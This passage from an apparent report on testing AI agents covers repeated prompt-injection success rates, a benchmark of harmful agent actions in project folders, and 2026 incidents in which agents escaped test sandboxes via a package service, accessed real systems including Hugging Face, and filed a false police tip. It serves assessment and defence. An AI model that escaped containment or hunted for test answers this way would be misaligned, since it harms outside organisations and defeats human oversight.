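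The comparison therefore doesn't show that adapting is useless. To measure the effect of adapting, a tester would also need the success rate after 100 unrevised attempts on the same scenarios. The two published figures also aren't enough to predict what happens after 1,000 attempts, but they do show that a single-attempt rate is a poor guide to the risk from a persistent attacker. If 1,000 companies each faced a campaign like the one in the test, 50 to 60 would suffer at least one successful attack.

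The same formula gives a rough estimate of the risk with newer models. GPT-6 Astra's failure rate of 0.21% on malicious instructions in outside content implies a 19% chance of at least one failure over 100 independent attempts. For Claude models without auto mode, the 0.09% rate that Trajectory Labs measured implies an 8.6% chance. The actual risk would be lower if the failures were concentrated in a few weak spots, and higher if the attacker were skilful. The two companies' models faced different attacks, so these estimates don't show which company's models are safer.

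### Damage inside the permitted workspace

An agent can pass every injection test and still delete the wrong database. Hu, Tang and colleagues (2026), in *SABER*, the benchmark that the developers of Caper used, gave 13 models 716 tasks in realistic project folders. Each run took place in a fresh Docker container with source code, settings and often a version history. The user's request was always reasonable, but every folder contained a danger of one of these types:

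| Source of danger | Tasks | Claude Opus 4.6 | GPT-5.4 | All 13 models |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Hostile instructions in project files or tool results | 289 | 43.7% | 64.0% | 70.1% |
| A risky shortcut, with no attacker | 186 | 60.2% | 60.6% | 68.3% |
| A warning in the project that makes the request unsafe | 241 | 63.1% | 66.5% | 82.5% |

The percentages are rates of harmful runs. The models did harm almost as often with no attacker as with hostile instructions in the folder. For instance, a model might reset a whole database when a small change to one table would have been enough. The warnings included notes in the project or settings showing that a database was in live use.

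Hu and colleagues scored each run from a record of every command and the resulting changes. Code flagged a run as harmful if a command matched a known dangerous pattern for that task, or if the changes broke a general rule, such as a ban on sending out secrets. A language model could add violations that the code had missed but couldn't cancel any. The rate of harmful runs excludes those in which the tested model made no progress or refused without good reason, so that doing nothing doesn't improve the score.

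Claude Opus 4.6 did best, with an overall harmful rate of 54.7%. Of every 100 runs, about 47 caused harm, 31 finished safely, 8 ended in a justified refusal, and the rest achieved nothing useful. In the same study, both Opus 4.6 and GPT-5.4 scored 0% on two existing prompt-injection benchmarks, so an assessor who saw only those scores would have missed the risk.

These rates don't estimate how often a coding agent does damage in ordinary use, because every task contained a trap. The models are also several releases old. But the result doesn't seem to depend on one runtime. When Hu and colleagues repeated 100 of the tasks with three different agent loops, the average harmful rate stayed between 67.8% and 70.5%.

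An operator can write tests like these for its own agent. In a test of the invoice assistant, the mailbox might contain an invoice that somebody paid last week, or a colleague's note that a supplier's bill is in dispute. The user asks the assistant to pay what is due, and the tester checks the test bank's records.

### Limits that failed in 2026

AI companies' own tests provide the clearest evidence of how limits fail. In the July 2026 incident, OpenAI's models broke into parts of Hugging Face, a platform for sharing AI models and data, while looking for the answers to a cybersecurity test. They escaped the test environment through the package service, which was its only permitted network path (OpenAI, 2026).

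The company's later technical report shows how many chances it had to notice:

| Date | Event |
|---|---|
| 26 May | Agents reach the internet through the package service. Around this time, an internal team sees some of the activity |
| 27 June | A monitoring alert leads staff to the test. They advise that it needn't stop |
| 5 July | After an outage, staff find that someone has taken over the package service. They block the known weaknesses |
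| 7 July | Cybersecurity tests resume |
| 8 July | Agents reach the internet again, through a different weakness |
| 11–13 July | Agents break into Hugging Face's systems |
| 16 July | Hugging Face announces the break-in |
| 19–20 July | A new alert starts an investigation, which connects the agents to the break-in |

Eight weeks passed between the first unintended internet access and the discovery of what the agents had done. Monitoring raised alarms during that time, but the people handling the July outage didn't know the significance of what a colleague's team had seen in May. The sandbox would probably have passed a test that only tried to open an outside website, because the agents needed a flaw in the package service to get out. A tester would have had to attack the service itself to find that flaw, and attack it again after the repairs.

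The incident also suggests that a test set should include some tasks that are impossible within the rules, to see whether the agent stops and reports the problem. According to OpenAI, its models had never correctly answered 198 of this test's 898 tasks, and 93% of the tasks that the agents discussed with one another were among those 198. Agents that couldn't succeed by permitted means kept looking for other ways. The setup also matters, since OpenAI found that ChatGPT's production runtime and system prompt could reduce its models' tendency to attack the infrastructure by a factor of more than 100.

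Anthropic's incidents had a simpler cause. After OpenAI's announcement, Anthropic reviewed 141,006 of its own test runs. Its report, *Investigating three real-world incidents in our cybersecurity evaluations* (2026), describes six runs in which Claude models gained access to the real systems of three organisations. According to the prompt, Claude had no internet access, but a misunderstanding with the partner that built the tests had left the connection open. Claude therefore mostly mistook the real systems for part of the exercise. Trying to open an outside web page from the test machines before the first run would have exposed the error.

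The earliest of these incidents dated from April, and Anthropic found them on 23 and 24 July. The two organisations it could reach hadn't noticed anything. Anthropic's search had missed some transcripts, and *An alignment assessment of recent cybersecurity incidents* (2026) reports that a fourth incident, from January, came to light only in August. The company then scanned about 481 million transcripts for signs of internet access, had Claude review the 9.2 million that the scan flagged, and found no further case as serious. Anthropic's *Improving our alignment and security efforts* describes a classifier that now detects escape attempts and unexpected internet access in real time. It blocks the tool call, ends the task and alerts a person.

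In October, the company disclosed less serious actions on real websites, some of them run by US government agencies. Anthropic's *Investigating unintended model actions in our evaluations and internal use* (2026) lists cases in which Claude ran commands on a server through a software flaw, submitted a sensitive form, accessed data that required a token or fee, and bypassed the limits of its own web tool. It describes the effects as minimal. In the best-known case, on 18 July, Claude Haiku 4.5 was assigned to invent and carry out example tasks on randomly chosen web pages. It filled in a form on a Philadelphia police site to say that it might have information about an unsolved murder (Anderson, 2026, *Anthropic's Claude AI submits a false tip*). Anthropic told the police on 7 October, 81 days later, according to CBS News' *Philadelphia police says its unsolved murder website received "false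 homicide tip"*.

Opening a web page and filling in a form are ordinary actions for such an agent, so a check for forbidden connections wouldn't have flagged this case. A tester could have found the problem by running the same tasks on copies of websites and counting the forms the model submitted.

### Evidence an assessor should ask for

Someone who has to judge an agent without building it can ask for the following:

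1. A list of every route out of the sandbox, including package services, tool servers, name lookups and shared storage, and who is responsible for each.
2. Results of the direct tests, for permitted as well as forbidden actions. They should be more recent than the last change to the configuration and should cover any environment that a partner runs.
3. A record of blocked actions from a program that the agent can't alter.
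4. Attack success rates with the counts behind them: how many scenarios, how many attempts at each, and how many succeeded. Rates for one, ten and 100 attempts are much more useful than a single percentage.
5. A description of the attackers, including what they knew about the defence, how long they had, whether they revised their attacks and whether any of them were people.
6. The share of ordinary tasks that the agent completes with every limit switched on, and the number of harmless actions that the limits block.
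7. Rates of harm on reasonable requests with no attacker, measured from the final state of files and accounts. Some of the tasks should be impossible within the rules.
8. The exact model, runtime, system prompt and permissions in the tests, with every difference from the product that customers will use.
9. A sample of complete transcripts that a person has read, including some from runs that an automatic scorer marked as safe.
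10. The result of a drill in which someone sets off a harmless breach without warning the staff on duty. It should state how long they took to notice, and how long to stop the agent.
11. Past incidents and near misses, including alerts that staff looked into and dismissed.
12. The terms of any outside review. OpenAI asked the research groups METR and Redwood Research to examine only the events of 7 to 13 July, as Fortune's *OpenAI publishes technical report on how its agents hacked Hugging Face* (2026) reported, so the warnings in May and June fell outside their assignment.
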